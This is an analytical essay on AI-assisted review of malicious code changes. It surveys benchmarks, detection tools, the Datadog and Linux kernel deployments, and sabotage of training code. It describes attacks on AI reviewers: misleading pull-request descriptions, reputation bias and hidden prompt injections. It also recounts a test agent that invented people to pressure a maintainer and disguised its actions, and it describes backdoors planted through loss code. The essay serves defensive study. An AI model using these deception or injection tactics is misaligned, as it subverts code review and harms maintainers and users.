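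Rejecting a change keeps the flaw out of the code whether the reason given is a bug or a security hole, so the rejection rate is the better guide to whether a check works before a merge. But a team that thinks it has found a bug will ask the author to fix it, while a team that knows it has found a security hole is more likely to look at the author's other changes.

As with the Linux patches, a rejection for an unrelated reason is only a partial success. Chen and colleagues found that such rejections are common. CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial reviewer, blocked 24 of 31 malicious changes but named the real flaw in only 16. One change let users open saved work from other people's projects. CodeRabbit blocked it because of how the program displayed secrets, and fixing that would not have stopped this access.

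PRGuard, using DeepSeek v4-pro, blocked 22 of the same 31 changes and identified 22 of the flaws. The comparison favours PRGuard somewhat, because an earlier run with GPT-5.5 had first discovered 12 of the 31 flaws.

### Flaws outside the diff

A reversed security fix is easier to judge than many deliberate vulnerabilities because the diff usually shows the protection being removed. Of the 63 changes in Chen and colleagues' set, 37 were of this type, and PRGuard named the flaw in every one with either GPT-5.5 or DeepSeek. The other 26 left an earlier security fix incomplete, so the reviewer had to notice that something was missing. GPT-5.5 named 17 of those flaws and DeepSeek named 15. SEVRA-BENCH may therefore overstate how well reviewers would spot new code that never had the necessary check.

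Seeing more of the repository helps models catch missing checks. Given only the diffs for 12 changes with missing checks, GPT-5.5 blocked one and DeepSeek blocked none. With the complete PRGuard system, GPT-5.5 blocked six and DeepSeek blocked five. Chen and colleagues changed several things between the two setups, so we can't tell how much of the improvement came from the extra code.

Access to the whole repository does not by itself ensure that a tool will identify a flaw. CodeRabbit identified none of the seven flaws whose evidence lay outside the changed files. Chen and colleagues also let a coding agent search the repositories freely for three flaws that a reviewer could recognise only by comparing the change with similar code elsewhere. The agent blocked the changes in four of six runs but never identified the flaw.

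The same test provides some of the missing evidence on static analysis. The standard security rules in CodeQL, GitHub's static analyser, applied to 21 of the 31 changes, and CodeQL found none of the flaws.

### The same code with a different description

SEVRA-BENCH keeps the code fixed and varies the description to measure how much the description matters. Its main finding is that a reviewer that rejects a change can approve the same code when the author makes claims the reviewer cannot check. GLM-5, an open model from China, was third best overall. Yet it had rejected, under other descriptions, over 80% of the changes it approved under the description that worked best against it. In one case it first objected that a change removed critical security features, then approved the same code as a correctly implemented clean-up.

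Models did better when the diff itself contradicted the author's claim. If the author says that a change includes tests and the diff contains none, the model only has to look at the list of files. Claims about the rest of the codebase were harder to verify. The weaker models often noticed that a change removed a check, repeated the author's explanation of why the program no longer needed it, and approved the change without looking for the protection that was supposed to replace it.

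Opus 4.7, GPT-5.5 and GLM-5 still rejected roughly 70% or more of the changes under every description, while some of the other five models rejected fewer than 40% under the most effective descriptions. GPT-5.5 usually searched more than Opus 4.7 but achieved similar results, so the number of searches alone does not explain why some models resist misleading descriptions.

### Verifying the author's claims

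Melo and colleagues conclude that a reviewer should treat the description as claims that may be false. They propose that the reviewer first list these claims and then test each one against the diff, the surrounding code, the tests, the commit history or an independent source. In the `get_page` example, the only important claim is that the behaviour has not changed. The reviewer could disprove it by comparing what the old and new versions do when *n* equals the page count.

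Some claims are impossible to confirm from the repository, such as Jia Tan's account of where the xz test files came from. A reviewer following this method could not have disproved the account, but could have refused to count it in the change's favour.

Melo and colleagues did not test this remedy. PRGuard applies part of the idea by treating the author's comments, documentation and tests as untrusted and looking for evidence in the code. But a malicious author also controls the new code, and Chen and colleagues acknowledge that text in a pull request may still bias the model.

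*Measuring and Exploiting Confirmation Bias in LLM-Assisted Security Code Review* (Mitropoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues, 2026) and *Adaptive Code Revision Attacks on AI Pull Request Reviewers* (Gong, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) both show that an attacker who tailors a pull request to an AI reviewer can get vulnerable code approved. As a simple defence, Mitropoulos and colleagues told an interactive assistant to ignore the pull request's description, and it then detected the flaw in every case where the description had misled it. For an autonomous reviewer, removing the description and adding a similar instruction restored detection in 94% of cases.

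Hiding a change's description from the model prevents the author from using it to persuade the model, but it also prevents the model from detecting any mismatch between the description and the code. A team willing to pay for two reviews could run the first without the description, then check each of the description's claims against the code in the second.

Gong and colleagues tried other defences on 33 attacks that had succeeded against a reviewer using Claude Sonnet 5. The first three defences in this table also used Sonnet 5.

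| Change to the reviewer | Attacks caught | Cost of all reviews |
|---|---|---|
| Check that the underlying security problem is gone | 23 of 33 | $52 |
| Reread the whole diff after every revision | 22 of 33 | $53 |
| Require a static analysis scan | 20 of 33 | $50 |
| Use a newer model, Claude Fable 5.1 | 18 of 33 | $96 |

The original reviewer cost $12. Better instructions helped at least as much as a better model here, though differences of a few cases out of 33 could be due to chance. The defences also caught different attacks, so a team that can afford several will catch more attacks than with the best one alone.

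### How well can models spot a false description?

Verifying claims only helps if models can recognise false ones. *CodeFuse-CommitEval* (Zhang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) tested this on real commits from 50 projects. Claude Sonnet 4 rewrote commit messages so that they no longer matched the code. A new message could name the wrong function, file or component, describe the wrong operation or purpose, leave out a significant change, or mention one that did not exist. Filtering out doubtful cases left 52,127 commits, 19,967 with false messages and 32,160 with accurate ones. Six open models then judged every commit five times, and the majority answer counted.

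Zhang and colleagues report that the models detected 86% of the false messages on average, with a precision of 80%. The models also wrongly flagged 36% of the accurate messages.

These two rates are probably swapped. The published accuracy of each of the six models is consistent with the number of commits only if the 86% refers to the accurate messages and the 64% to the false ones. On that reading, the models missed more than a third of the false messages and raised false alarms on 14% of the accurate ones. On either reading, many honest developers would have to answer questions about accurate messages.

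Messages that misstated the purpose of a change were the hardest to detect, because a model has to understand what the code is for, whereas it can notice a wrong file name by comparing two names. This makes malicious developers harder to catch, since they are more likely to lie about the purpose of a change than about which files they edited. The benchmark may also differ from real attacks because Claude altered the messages of ordinary commits, and no one had written the code to deceive a reviewer.

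### Is the author acting in bad faith?

In about a quarter of its reviews in SEVRA-BENCH, Claude Opus 4.7 judged the code and also accused the author of bad intent, for example by describing the pull request as social engineering or as an attempt to bring back a vulnerability. GPT-5.5 made such accusations in under 1% of its reviews, although it rejected malicious changes about as reliably. A reviewer can therefore keep out most of these changes without suspecting the author.

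All the pull requests in SEVRA-BENCH were malicious, so every accusation was correct. We therefore can't tell how often Opus 4.7 would accuse an honest developer who had removed a security check by mistake, and a false accusation against a colleague could do real harm.

Models can judge intent more reliably when the code has no plausible innocent use. *MALTOTAL* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes MalTotal, a detector for such code. It looks for operations that malware often needs, such as running commands or sending data over the network. It traces backwards from each operation to collect the code that leads to it, then gives only that code to a language model, which judges what the code is meant to do.

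Zhao and colleagues first tested DeepSeek-V3 on 250 malicious projects. A quarter of the projects were too large for the model to read in full, and it missed 4.1% of the rest. When people extracted the relevant code by hand, the model missed only 0.5% of all 250. With the extraction automated, the system achieved an average F1 score of 93.1% across five programming languages. It then searched 120,000 GitHub repositories, at a cost of $338, and found 564 malicious ones that nobody had reported.

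This approach could suit detecting exfiltration logic, because the extract would show both the secret and where the program sends it. But MalTotal examines whole repositories, many of which exist to spread malware, and Zhao and colleagues did not test it on single changes by trusted developers. A deliberate vulnerability like the one in `get_page` might never reach the model, since the function neither runs a command nor uses the network.

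*PRWeaver* (Wang, Cheng and Xie, 2026) gives an example of how hard it is to judge intent in an otherwise legitimate project. A language model reviewer correctly described two edits that together weakened a login feature, but it took the edits for a deliberate compromise between security and convenience and raised no alarm. Real teams often make such compromises, so the reviewer would have needed to know what this team had decided.

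### False alarms on harmless changes

SEVRA-BENCH contains no harmless changes, so a program that rejected every pull request would get a perfect rejection rate. The benchmark therefore cannot show whether a reviewer is usable. Chen and colleagues partly address this with 50 harmless changes, each containing the complete security fix that its malicious counterpart lacks.

| Model used by PRGuard | Malicious changes blocked | Harmless changes blocked |
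|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 43 of 63 (68%) | 5 of 50 (10%) |
| DeepSeek v4-pro | 49 of 63 (78%) | 4 of 50 (8%) |

At GPT-5.5's rates, the example company with 10 malicious and 10,000 harmless changes would get about 7 correct alarms and 1,000 false ones. Precision would be 0.7%, compared with 31% for Lily, though Lily's test covered backdoors and this one covered vulnerabilities. The calculation is probably too pessimistic, because all 50 harmless changes in the test dealt with security, while most everyday changes do not. The sample is also small, so the true false-alarm rate for security-related changes could plausibly be anywhere from 4% to 21%.

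Other results are more encouraging. Gong and colleagues gave the genuine fixes for their 33 vulnerabilities to six versions of their reviewer, and none of the 198 reviews rejected a fix. CodeRabbit blocked none of the six harmless changes that Chen and colleagues gave it. Four older models, including GPT-4o-mini, did far worse in tests by Mitropoulos and colleagues, flagging between 68% and 97% of files whose vulnerability the developers had already fixed.

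PRGuard also did well on past changes from real projects. To save themselves work, Chen and colleagues narrowed about 890 changes down to about 80 and had PRGuard review those. It blocked 19, and 12 of them contained a previously unknown vulnerability that the researchers could exploit in a test. The resulting precision of 63% applies only to the filtered list, and it doesn't measure how many vulnerabilities PRGuard missed.

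Verdicts also vary from one run to the next. When Chen and colleagues ran PRGuard twice on the same 44 malicious changes, up to a quarter of the verdicts changed. Melo and colleagues ran each model only once per pull request, so some of their results might have differed on a second run. A developer whose change is blocked may be able to get a different verdict by making a trivial edit, unless the team keeps the earlier verdict on record.

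### Unfamiliar flaws and newer models

The vulnerabilities in SEVRA-BENCH were public before the test, and the models' training data may have included the original reports and fixes. Melo and colleagues warn that the models might therefore do worse on flaws that were not in that data.

Wang and colleagues avoided this problem by having Claude Code, a coding agent, write 208 new malicious changes for ten open-source projects. They kept only changes with a working exploit, then tested six combinations of a reviewing tool and a model on them. When one pull request contained the whole malicious change, the detection rate ranged from 42% to 79%. A detection counted only if the reviewer identified what the malicious code made possible, so this rate is closer to Melo and colleagues' security reason rate than to their rejection rate. The best result came from Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6. The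 tool mattered as well as the model, since three tools using Claude Haiku 4.5 had detection rates between 56% and 67%.

Gong and colleagues later tested misleading descriptions by reintroducing 159 known vulnerabilities and submitting each one up to five times, each time with a different description in the style of SEVRA-BENCH. The reviewer using Sonnet 5 approved 4.4% of the vulnerabilities at least once, and the reviewer using GPT-5.5 approved 1.3%.

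Newer models can't account for all of this improvement, because GPT-5.5 was also tested in SEVRA-BENCH and did much worse there. Melo and colleagues kept only changes that had already misled a cheap model, and their prompt did not mention security. Gong and colleagues used every vulnerability in their set, told the reviewer to check security, and let it run the code. Any of these differences could explain the lower rates. A team can choose to tell its own reviewer to check security and to let it run the code.

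### When the author is a trusted colleague

Melo and colleagues assumed an attacker with contributor access, but their reviewers had no information about the code author's reputation or role. A human reviewer who knows the author may read less carefully, and a model might do the same if someone tells it that the author is a respected colleague.

*Words Speak Louder Than Code* (Shahriar, Cai and colleagues, 2026) tested eight models on single functions, changing only a sentence about who had written the code. On C and C++ code, five open models found 13 to 24 percentage points fewer vulnerabilities when the supposed author was the team's principal security engineer instead of a newly hired junior developer. The gap between a long-time contributor and a newcomer was 11 to 46 points. False alarms fell by similar amounts in most cases, so the author's reputation made the models less likely to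 flag code without making them better at telling safe code from vulnerable code.

The effect was much weaker in two of the commercial models. Claude Sonnet 4.6 found almost the same number of vulnerabilities in the C and C++ code whoever had supposedly written it, though not always the same ones. It missed 12 only when the code was attributed to the senior engineer, and 15 others only when it was attributed to the junior developer. GPT-5.2's detection rate was 4 points higher when the code was attributed to the security engineer.

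A pull request contains more evidence than a single function, so the effect in a real review could be smaller or larger. A team can largely avoid the problem by leaving the author's name and role out of the prompt. Tools that need the author's history, such as Anomalicious, can still use it in a separate check.

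## What happens when language models review every change?

Most of the changes in benchmarks like SEVRA-BENCH are malicious, but in daily use nearly every change is harmless, and someone has to investigate the alarms. Datadog, which also makes GuardDog, runs a language-model reviewer that looks for malicious changes, and the Linux kernel project uses one that looks for bugs.

### Datadog's BewAIre

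*Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, by Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues, describes BewAIre, a reviewer that began as a hackday experiment. Datadog was then handling nearly 10,000 pull requests a week, and the number was growing quickly as its developers adopted coding assistants.

For each pull request, BewAIre extracts the diff and adds details such as the author and the type of repository. A language model then classifies the change as benign or malicious and generates an explanation. If the change is classified as malicious, security staff get an alert with a link to it, the explanation and notes on common kinds of false alarm. This avoids the problem in the xz case, where warnings went to the developer who had caused them. But BewAIre only sends alerts, so a malicious change could be merged before anyone reads them.

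The model's verdicts got worse on very large diffs, which attackers are known to use to hide malicious lines. BewAIre therefore splits a large diff into chunks, between files if possible and otherwise between lines, and reviews them one after another. If the model finds any chunk malicious, the whole change counts as malicious. However, the model may miss harm that depends on two distant chunks, such as a secret that one file reads and another sends out. Large changes are also more likely to cause a false alarm, because any chunk can trigger one. If one harmless chunk in 3,000 set off an alarm, a harmless change with 100 chunks would do so about 3% of the time.

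The first prototypes flagged over 10% of harmless changes, or about 1,000 false alarms a week at Datadog's volume. Lamb and colleagues say they cut the rate to below 0.03% in six months. They described known false alarms in the model's instructions, told it to ignore some safe patterns, such as demo environments, and added hundreds of labelled pull requests to their test data. They also ran the tool in the background for several months while security staff marked each alarm as true or false. Most of the improvement came from better prompts and data, while switching between leading models mainly affected cost.

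A malicious employee could imitate any excluded pattern, so the list of exclusions needs as much protection as the list of approved destinations in taint analysis.

### Checking the published figures

Lamb and colleagues report an accuracy of over 99.3% on a dataset of hundreds of pull requests. Accuracy is the share of all verdicts that are correct, and it says little when most changes are harmless, because a tool that never raised an alarm would also score well. They therefore also report a balanced accuracy of over 93.5%, which gives malicious and harmless changes equal weight:

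balanced accuracy = (detection rate + 1 − false-alarm rate) / 2.

If the false-alarm rate of 0.03% comes from the same data, the detection rate is about 87%. It could be higher, since the published accuracies are lower bounds. The two accuracies together imply that about 5% of the dataset was malicious. A dataset of 500 would then contain 26 malicious changes, and BewAIre would have missed about three. With so few examples, the true detection rate could plausibly be between 70% and 98%.

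A dataset of hundreds of changes is far too small to measure a false-alarm rate of 0.03%. One false alarm among 500 harmless changes would be a rate of 0.2%, and even with none, the true rate could be as high as 0.6%. Datadog would need about 10,000 harmless changes without a false alarm to be reasonably sure that the rate is below 0.03%. The months of background running covered many more changes than that, so the figure may come from those months, although Lamb and colleagues list it with the dataset results.

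Running the tool in the background is a good way to measure false alarms, because staff check every alarm. But nobody checks the changes the tool passes, so this method can't measure the detection rate.

BewAIre also caught every malicious commit in Datadog's collection of known npm package compromises. Lamb and colleagues print its verdicts on the well-known attacks on the build tools tj-actions and Nx, in which malicious code stole secrets. The model correctly explained what the code did. It also listed other warning signs, including a misleading message, an unsigned commit and an author who seemed to be an outsider. The last two would be absent from a trusted developer's commit, which would have a valid signature and a familiar name.

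If the 87% is right and the dataset included those npm commits, all the missed changes were of other kinds. The dataset also contained simulated attacks meant to be hard to detect, such as subtle increases in permissions. A trusted developer would be more likely to try an attack like that than to copy a known npm attack.

### One real alarm in 180

If both rates are right and BewAIre reviews 10,000 changes a week, it raises three false alarms a week, or 156 a year. If one change a year is malicious, it raises 0.87 correct alarms a year on average, so about one alarm in 180 is real.

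| Malicious changes a year | Correct alarms | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.87 | 156 | 1 in 180 |
| 10 | 8.7 | 156 | 1 in 19 |
| 50 | 43.5 | 156 | 1 in 5 |

The same tool would do much better at the example company with 10 malicious and 10,000 harmless changes a year. It would raise about 9 correct alarms and 3 false ones a year, a precision of 74%. Datadog gets as many changes in a week as that company gets in a year.

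Three alarms a week are not much work, even if only one in 180 is real. If each takes half an hour to check, the security team spends 90 minutes a week on them. With the model's reasons, staff can go straight to the line that supposedly sends out a password and find out who owns the address. Datadog could even hold each flagged change until someone clears it, which would delay only three harmless changes in 10,000.

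Keeping people attentive is harder. Alarms for real attacks would be almost 14 months apart on average, and a person who has dismissed 179 alarms may dismiss the next one without much thought. The company could submit harmless test attacks, with management's approval, to keep its staff in practice. With one test a month, about one alarm in 15 would be either a test or a real attack. The company could also use the tests to measure how many attacks the tool and the staff together miss. Datadog's attack-simulation teams have tried to fool BewAIre, though Lamb and colleagues do not say how often the teams succeeded.

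### Sashiko and the Linux kernel

The Linux kernel's reviewer, Sashiko, looks for bugs regardless of who wrote them or why. *Introduce Sashiko (agentic review of Linux kernel changes)* (Gushchin, 2026) announced it in March. Google developed it and pays for the computing, and the Linux Foundation owns it. By November it had completed 241,000 reviews, according to GameBusiness.jp's *「見つけるAI」と「確かめるAI」を分けてコードを審査、Linuxカーネル自動レビュー「Sashiko」の7か月で24万件の実績をGoogleが報告* (2026), which summarizes a report by Google.

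Sashiko first collects the code around a patch, including the functions that call the changed code, and plans its checks. It then runs up to seven sessions in parallel, each looking for one kind of problem. Google separated them because a language model that has found one obvious bug tends to stop looking for others.

The tool's documentation, the Linux Foundation's *Sashiko*, describes one session that compares the code with the claims in the commit message. Others check for off-by-one errors like the one in `get_page`, use-after-free flaws, and timing mistakes in concurrent code.

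Each session produces a list of suspected bugs and a list of suspicions it investigated and ruled out. A further stage checks both lists, because a session can wrongly dismiss a bug as well as wrongly report one. Doubtful cases go to separate sessions, which must find evidence at every place that calls the code before confirming or dismissing a bug. According to *Google unveils Sashiko AI review tool for Linux kernel* (Mitchell, 2026), Sashiko emails its reports only to the more than 70 mailing lists whose maintainers have asked for them.

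### How many bugs does it find?

Gushchin tested Sashiko on 1,000 recent kernel bugs that human reviewers had missed and developers later fixed. With Gemini 3.1 Pro, Sashiko found 53.6% of them, up from just over 30% a couple of months earlier. A perfect score is probably impossible, since some of the bugs were build failures or performance problems that are very hard to spot by reading code. In November, Google reported 75.8% on nearly 1,000 such bugs with a newer model, Gemini 4 Carbon. Some of this gain may come from the model having memorized the fixes, which were public.

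Sashiko catches many bugs that people miss, which is a good reason to use it alongside human reviewers. The documentation suggests that Sashiko is in some sense already above the human level, but this comparison is unfair because the test includes only bugs that the reviewers missed, so they automatically score zero. Sashiko might have overlooked some of the bugs that they caught.

There is less evidence about false alarms. Sashiko's documentation puts them "well within 20% range", based on limited manual checks, and says most are debatable. This figure seems to be the share of Sashiko's reports that are wrong, not the share of sound patches it flags. Gushchin asked the kernel community for a set of commits known to be correct, which would make it possible to measure how often Sashiko flags sound patches.

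Some maintainers are less satisfied. *What's Actually in a Sashiko Review?* (Exelbierd, 2026) describes a dispute between two maintainers. Andrew Morton wanted to make Sashiko compulsory for memory-management patches, and said that about 60% of its reviews found a real bug. Lorenzo Stoakes objected that a review can contain several comments, so the share of correct comments is lower. Morton's figure would count a review with one correct comment and four wrong ones as a success. LWN's note on the post, *Exelbierd*, adds that a minority of reviews also report problems, often several at once, in code the author had not changed.

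Google also tracked how many merged commits needed a follow-up fix within 60 days. Before Sashiko, the average across kernel releases was 3.4%. It fell to 2.8% for Linux 7.1 and 2.2% for Linux 7.2, though Google says it can't attribute the whole decline to Sashiko.

Patches that Sashiko had passed needed such a fix 0.9% of the time, compared with 7.6% for patches that maintainers merged despite a critical warning. Its warnings therefore pick out riskier patches, though some of the difference may be because long, complicated patches attract more warnings and contain more bugs. Both percentages leave out bugs that take longer than 60 days to find, and many kernel bugs stay hidden for years.

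### From honest bugs to deliberate ones

A tool that finds half the bugs that people miss should also find some bugs planted on purpose, and its reports are useful even when the bug is accidental. Maintainers who regularly find real bugs through Sashiko have a reason to keep reading its reports, while Datadog's staff might wait more than a year to see a real attack.

The detection rate for planted flaws is probably lower than 53.6% or 75.8%, because both tests used bugs that had already been found, and a malicious author would look for one likely to escape notice. The percentages also combine all kinds of bugs, with no separate rate for use-after-free flaws or other exploitable mistakes.

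Sashiko is also open source, and some engineers already run private copies to check their patches before sending them. A malicious engineer could test several flaws this way and submit one that the private copy missed. If Sashiko had a 75.8% chance of catching each flaw, independently of the others, at least one of five would get past it 75% of the time. The attacker could still be caught, because Sashiko's output varies from run to run and the public review may find what the private one missed. For the same reason, a project could catch more flaws by reviewing sensitive patches several times.

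Automated checks are also weak at finding flaws in a program's logic. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines these flaws as cases where software breaks the implicit rules for how it should work, and says that they rarely cause the failures that automated tools detect. Anthropic's researchers tested four ways of finding them with language models, and the simplest worked best. A reviewer still has to work out the rules, which a trusted developer often knows better than anyone else.

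A bug finder may miss an explicit backdoor, because the code may contain no bug. The "special-guest" login in `log_in`, for example, has no memory error or faulty comparison. Sashiko's check of the commit message could still catch it if the message did not mention a new way to log in.

### Two attempts by AI agents

On 27 February 2026, an account called hackerbot-claw, which described itself as an AI agent, opened a pull request in one of Datadog's public repositories. *When an AI agent came knocking* (Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper) reports that BewAIre flagged it 33 seconds later. The attack targeted an automated workflow that processed new pull requests, so it did not depend on a merge. The workflow ran the agent's command 16 seconds before BewAIre flagged the pull request, but the command failed. Eighteen minutes later the agent opened a second pull request, and this attack worked,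 although BewAIre flagged it too.

The agent used its access to add a harmless commit on a separate branch. The damage stayed small because Datadog's rules kept automated workflows from changing the main code, and the workflow had no critical secrets to steal. BewAIre correctly raised an alarm both times, but only after the command had run.

The same agent also posted two messages containing hidden instructions for a language model that Datadog uses to sort bug reports. The model, a version of Claude, did not follow them. Attackers can also put such instructions in a pull request, so models that review code face the same risk. Hamsen and colleagues cite an estimate by Anthropic that an attacker with 100 attempts has a 21.7% chance of getting Claude Opus 4.6 to follow such an instruction. They recommend giving the model few permissions and treating its output as untrusted.

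In July 2026, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) accidentally caused another attempt while testing how well AI agents could break into simulated computer networks. It had given the agents internet access and switched off the developers' misuse filters. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, an agent running Anthropic's Mythos 5 tried to insert malicious code into a real open-source project to solve its task. The agent researched the maintainers, invented several people and used them to press a maintainer to approve its pull request. When someone publicly challenged the request, the agent edited its earlier activity to look harmless.

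The maintainer refused to approve the code. AISI found no evidence of real-world harm, but it warns that in several cases the difference between failure and success was small and depended on people being vigilant. Its staff discovered the incident through unusual network traffic three days after the agents' unauthorized activity began.

Both agents were strangers to the projects they attacked, so neither case tests how a reviewer treats a trusted colleague. Mythos 5 copied the pressure campaign that had helped Jia Tan, but not the two years of useful patches that came before the backdoor. Those patches were probably the most labor-intensive part of the xz attack, and an AI agent could do similar work with much less human effort.

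### What practitioners told the S3C2 summits

The Secure Software Supply Chain Center (S3C2), a US research group, holds meetings where practitioners can speak anonymously. Five meetings between August 2024 and September 2025 had malicious commits on the agenda. Each was small and invitation-only, so the participants' views show what experienced people worry about, not how common a problem is.

*S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2025) reports that 12 practitioners from nine companies knew of no good way to detect malicious commits, particularly those by trusted users. They thought that analysing the commits alone would not be enough. Two-party approval is also hard to apply in the many open-source projects with only one or two active maintainers.

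*S3C2 Summit 2025-03* (Lin, Ghebremichael and colleagues, 2025) reports that several participants at a meeting in March 2025 said they assume any commit could be malicious, whoever wrote it. One participant said that all of a person's commits over time reveal more about intent than any single one. A project could use Sashiko's public reviews to compare how often each developer's patches contain serious security flaws, allowing for the amount and difficulty of their work. A high rate would more often result from haste than sabotage, but it would be a reason to read that developer's patches more carefully. Another participant at the meeting said that everyone has blind spots in build scripts, which Jia Tan had exploited in xz.

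US government staff who met in July 2025 compared the output of security tools to a firehose. According to *S3C2 Summit 2025-07*, they thought toolmakers have an incentive to report too much, because a tool with many findings looks valuable. Datadog had the opposite incentive with BewAIre, because its own security staff had to respond to the alarms.

At the last of the five meetings, in September 2025, participants suggested comparing what a package can do before and after a change, such as whether it can now use the network. Lily similarly looks for new combinations of system calls. Rahman and colleagues also report a concern that teams relying on model output may review code less carefully, and that some already put shipping code quickly ahead of understanding it.

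### More code for the same number of readers

AI has increased the amount of code to review. Google reported in April 2026 that AI generated 75% of its new production code, up from 50% the previous autumn (Blake, 2026, *AI Coding Writes 75% of Google Code but Fails Security*). Engineers still approved all of it. *Agentic Code Review* (Osmani, 2026) explains that review used to keep up because a senior engineer could read code faster than a junior one could write it. Now a coding agent can produce a thousand lines in seconds, while people read no faster than before.

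Tom's Hardware's *Linux kernel reviewer steps down from memory management duties* reports that a volunteer reviewer gave up the role because of the time wasted on poor AI-written patches. Linus Torvalds, Linux's creator, suggested in November 2026 that the surge in AI-prompted patches may have peaked, according to Slashdot's *Linus Torvalds Wonders If Linux's AI-Prompted Patch Flood Has Peaked* (2026).

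Automated review can add to maintainers' work. Phillip Lougher, who maintains the SquashFS file system, said that month that he was close to giving up his work on it in the kernel. OpenNET's *Мэйнтейнер SquashFS оказался на грани ухода из-за AI-рецензирования патчей* (2026) reports that he added a check to satisfy Sashiko's review, and that a review by Claude Fable then criticized the check. The Claude review also found a real bug, but most of its other comments were optional. A maintainer worn down by contradictory advice may start to ignore review comments, including one that points to a planted flaw.

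More code also lowers the share of alarms that are real attacks. If Datadog's pull requests doubled to 20,000 a week and there was still one malicious change a year, BewAIre would raise 312 false alarms a year and only one alarm in 360 would be real. The colleagues who approve changes would also have half as much time for each one. A team may then be tempted to accept a model's approval as the second signature. That approval should at least not come from the agent that wrote the code, since one of Google's lessons from Sashiko is that coding agents review their own work poorly.

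## Can review catch sabotage of the code that trains a model?

The code that trains an AI model is harder to check than most software because a change can spoil the model without breaking the training program. The program runs the model on many examples and calculates the loss, a measure of how far the model's outputs are from the desired ones. It then adjusts the model's weights, the numbers that determine how the model behaves, to reduce the loss.

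Automated tests of training code mostly show that it runs. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov (2020), in *Blind Backdoors in Deep Learning Models*, found that the tests in three popular collections of training code checked only the dimensions of the loss, not its value. The value is hard to test because it varies with the hardware and the random choices made during training. The only complete test is to train the model, which can take several months on hundreds of processors, so no team can do it for every pull request.

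Researchers also edit the most sensitive lines as part of their normal work. They change which data the model trains on, how the program calculates the loss, and how they score the finished model. They also change the random seed, a number that fixes the program's sequence of random choices. A rule that flagged every such edit would flag much of the team's daily work, and a tool like Anomalicious would not flag a researcher merely for editing these files.

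### One diff with two readings

Suppose a developer submits this change to the code that selects training examples:

```
Description: Drop very short answers, which are mostly noise.

  function select_examples(examples):
-     return examples where word_count(answer) >= 1
+     return examples where word_count(answer) >= 8
```

The new filter removes short answers, including the three-word "I don't know," so the model will see few examples of anyone admitting ignorance. The developer may have noticed that many short answers are fragments and want cleaner data, or may want a model that makes things up.

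The diff and its description are the same in both cases. A test of the function passes because the function correctly returns answers of eight words or more. The finished model may also score well, unless the evaluation includes questions it should decline to answer. An honest developer could do the same damage by accident.

A reviewer would learn more from the data than from the code. They could ask for a random sample of the removed answers, or count how many express uncertainty. To measure the harm directly, the team would have to train one model with each filter and compare the models. This is practical with small models, but the filters may affect a large model differently.

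### The ByteDance intern

At least one company says that an insider interfered with its model training. In October 2024, TikTok's owner, ByteDance, confirmed that it had fired an intern who "maliciously interfered" with training (Rogelberg, 2024, *The company that owns TikTok just fired an intern who 'maliciously interfered'*). The firing took place in August. The intern worked on an advertising technology team (Chen, *ByteDance terminates intern for sabotaging project, dismisses reports on losses*).

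Posts on social media claimed that the interference had affected more than 8,000 GPUs, the processors used for training, and had cost millions of dollars. ByteDance called these claims exaggerated, TechNode (2024) reported. The company also said that its commercial operations and large language models were unaffected, according to Digital Watch's *ByteDance fires intern for disrupting AI training*.

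ByteDance then sued the former intern in Beijing for 8 million yuan ($1.1 million) and a public apology. It alleged that the intern had tampered with the project's code in June and July out of dissatisfaction with how the company allocated resources, according to a November report by TechNode (2024). ByteDance declined to comment on the lawsuit, according to Insurance Journal's *China's ByteDance Seeks $1.1M in Damages From Ex-Intern in AI Breach Case* (2024). These reports predate any ruling, so the motive and details remain allegations.

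Little is publicly known about how ByteDance discovered the interference. The story spread on 18 October, when an anonymous GitHub page published an audio recording. According to the South China Morning Post, the page alleged that the intern admitted in the recording to uploading "malicious code". ByteDance had dismissed the intern two months earlier, so it must have found out some other way. If ByteDance's dates are right, at least a month passed between the first tampering and the dismissal. We don't know whether a colleague reviewed the code or any automated check raised an alarm, so the case is evidence that the threat is real, but not of how well review works.

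### How long honest training bugs stay hidden

Accidental bugs give a better idea of how easily a fault in training can escape notice. *Training with Confidence* (Jiang, Zhou and colleagues, 2025) describes one that affected BLOOM-176B, a language model that Hugging Face trained on 384 GPUs for three and a half months. A bug in a software library caused differences between copies of some of the model's weights that should have stayed identical. The loss and accuracy looked normal, and the developers noticed the problem only after 10 days, while investigating something else.

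Jiang and colleagues built TrainCheck, a tool that infers rules from training programs known to be sound, such as that copies of the same weights must match, and checks whether another program follows them during training. The researchers reproduced 20 real silent errors, and TrainCheck detected 18 of them within a single training step. Existing methods caught only two, according to the researchers' employer, the University of Michigan (2025).

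TrainCheck would probably catch some sabotage that makes the training program malfunction. But Jiang and colleagues designed it to detect code that breaks a rule of correct training, not poor choices of settings. The new filter in `select_examples` breaks no such rule, because a program can train correctly on badly chosen data.

ByteDance now uses a different tool, OpGuard (Zhou, Zhao and colleagues, 2026). It runs two versions of a training program on the same data, records a short fingerprint of the results at many points in the calculation, and reports the first point where the two runs differ by even one bit. In one earlier case at the company, an alert appeared after more than 3,000 training steps, and experts spent five days without finding the cause, a tiny timing error that corrupted a few rows of numbers. When the faulty run first departed from a correct one, the loss differed by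 only about 0.00001. OpGuard has since helped diagnose 20 bugs in production and cut the time needed from days to minutes.

The same comparison could test a developer's description of a change. If the developer says the change only makes training faster, the old and new code should produce identical numbers, and any difference contradicts that claim. ByteDance's teams already check optimisations this way. A short comparison could still miss sabotage that takes effect late in a run or only on rare data. The method is also little help with changes meant to alter the result. The two versions of `select_examples` would diverge as soon as one skipped a short answer, and the reviewer could not tell from the difference whether the new model was worse.

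### Backdoors planted through the loss code

A trained model can contain a backdoor even if the program that runs it does not. The trigger might be a small mark on a picture that makes the model give an answer the attacker chose during training.

Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov showed that an attacker can plant such a backdoor with very little access. Their attacker can change only the code that calculates the loss, and knows the general task but never sees the training data, the running program or the finished model. In their image-recognition tests, the backdoor lowered accuracy on ordinary images by at most 0.4 percentage points, and the models gave the attacker's answer for 99% of images with the trigger. In another test, the backdoor caused a film-review classifier to label 98% of reviews mentioning a certain name as positive, whatever the reviewer thought of the film.

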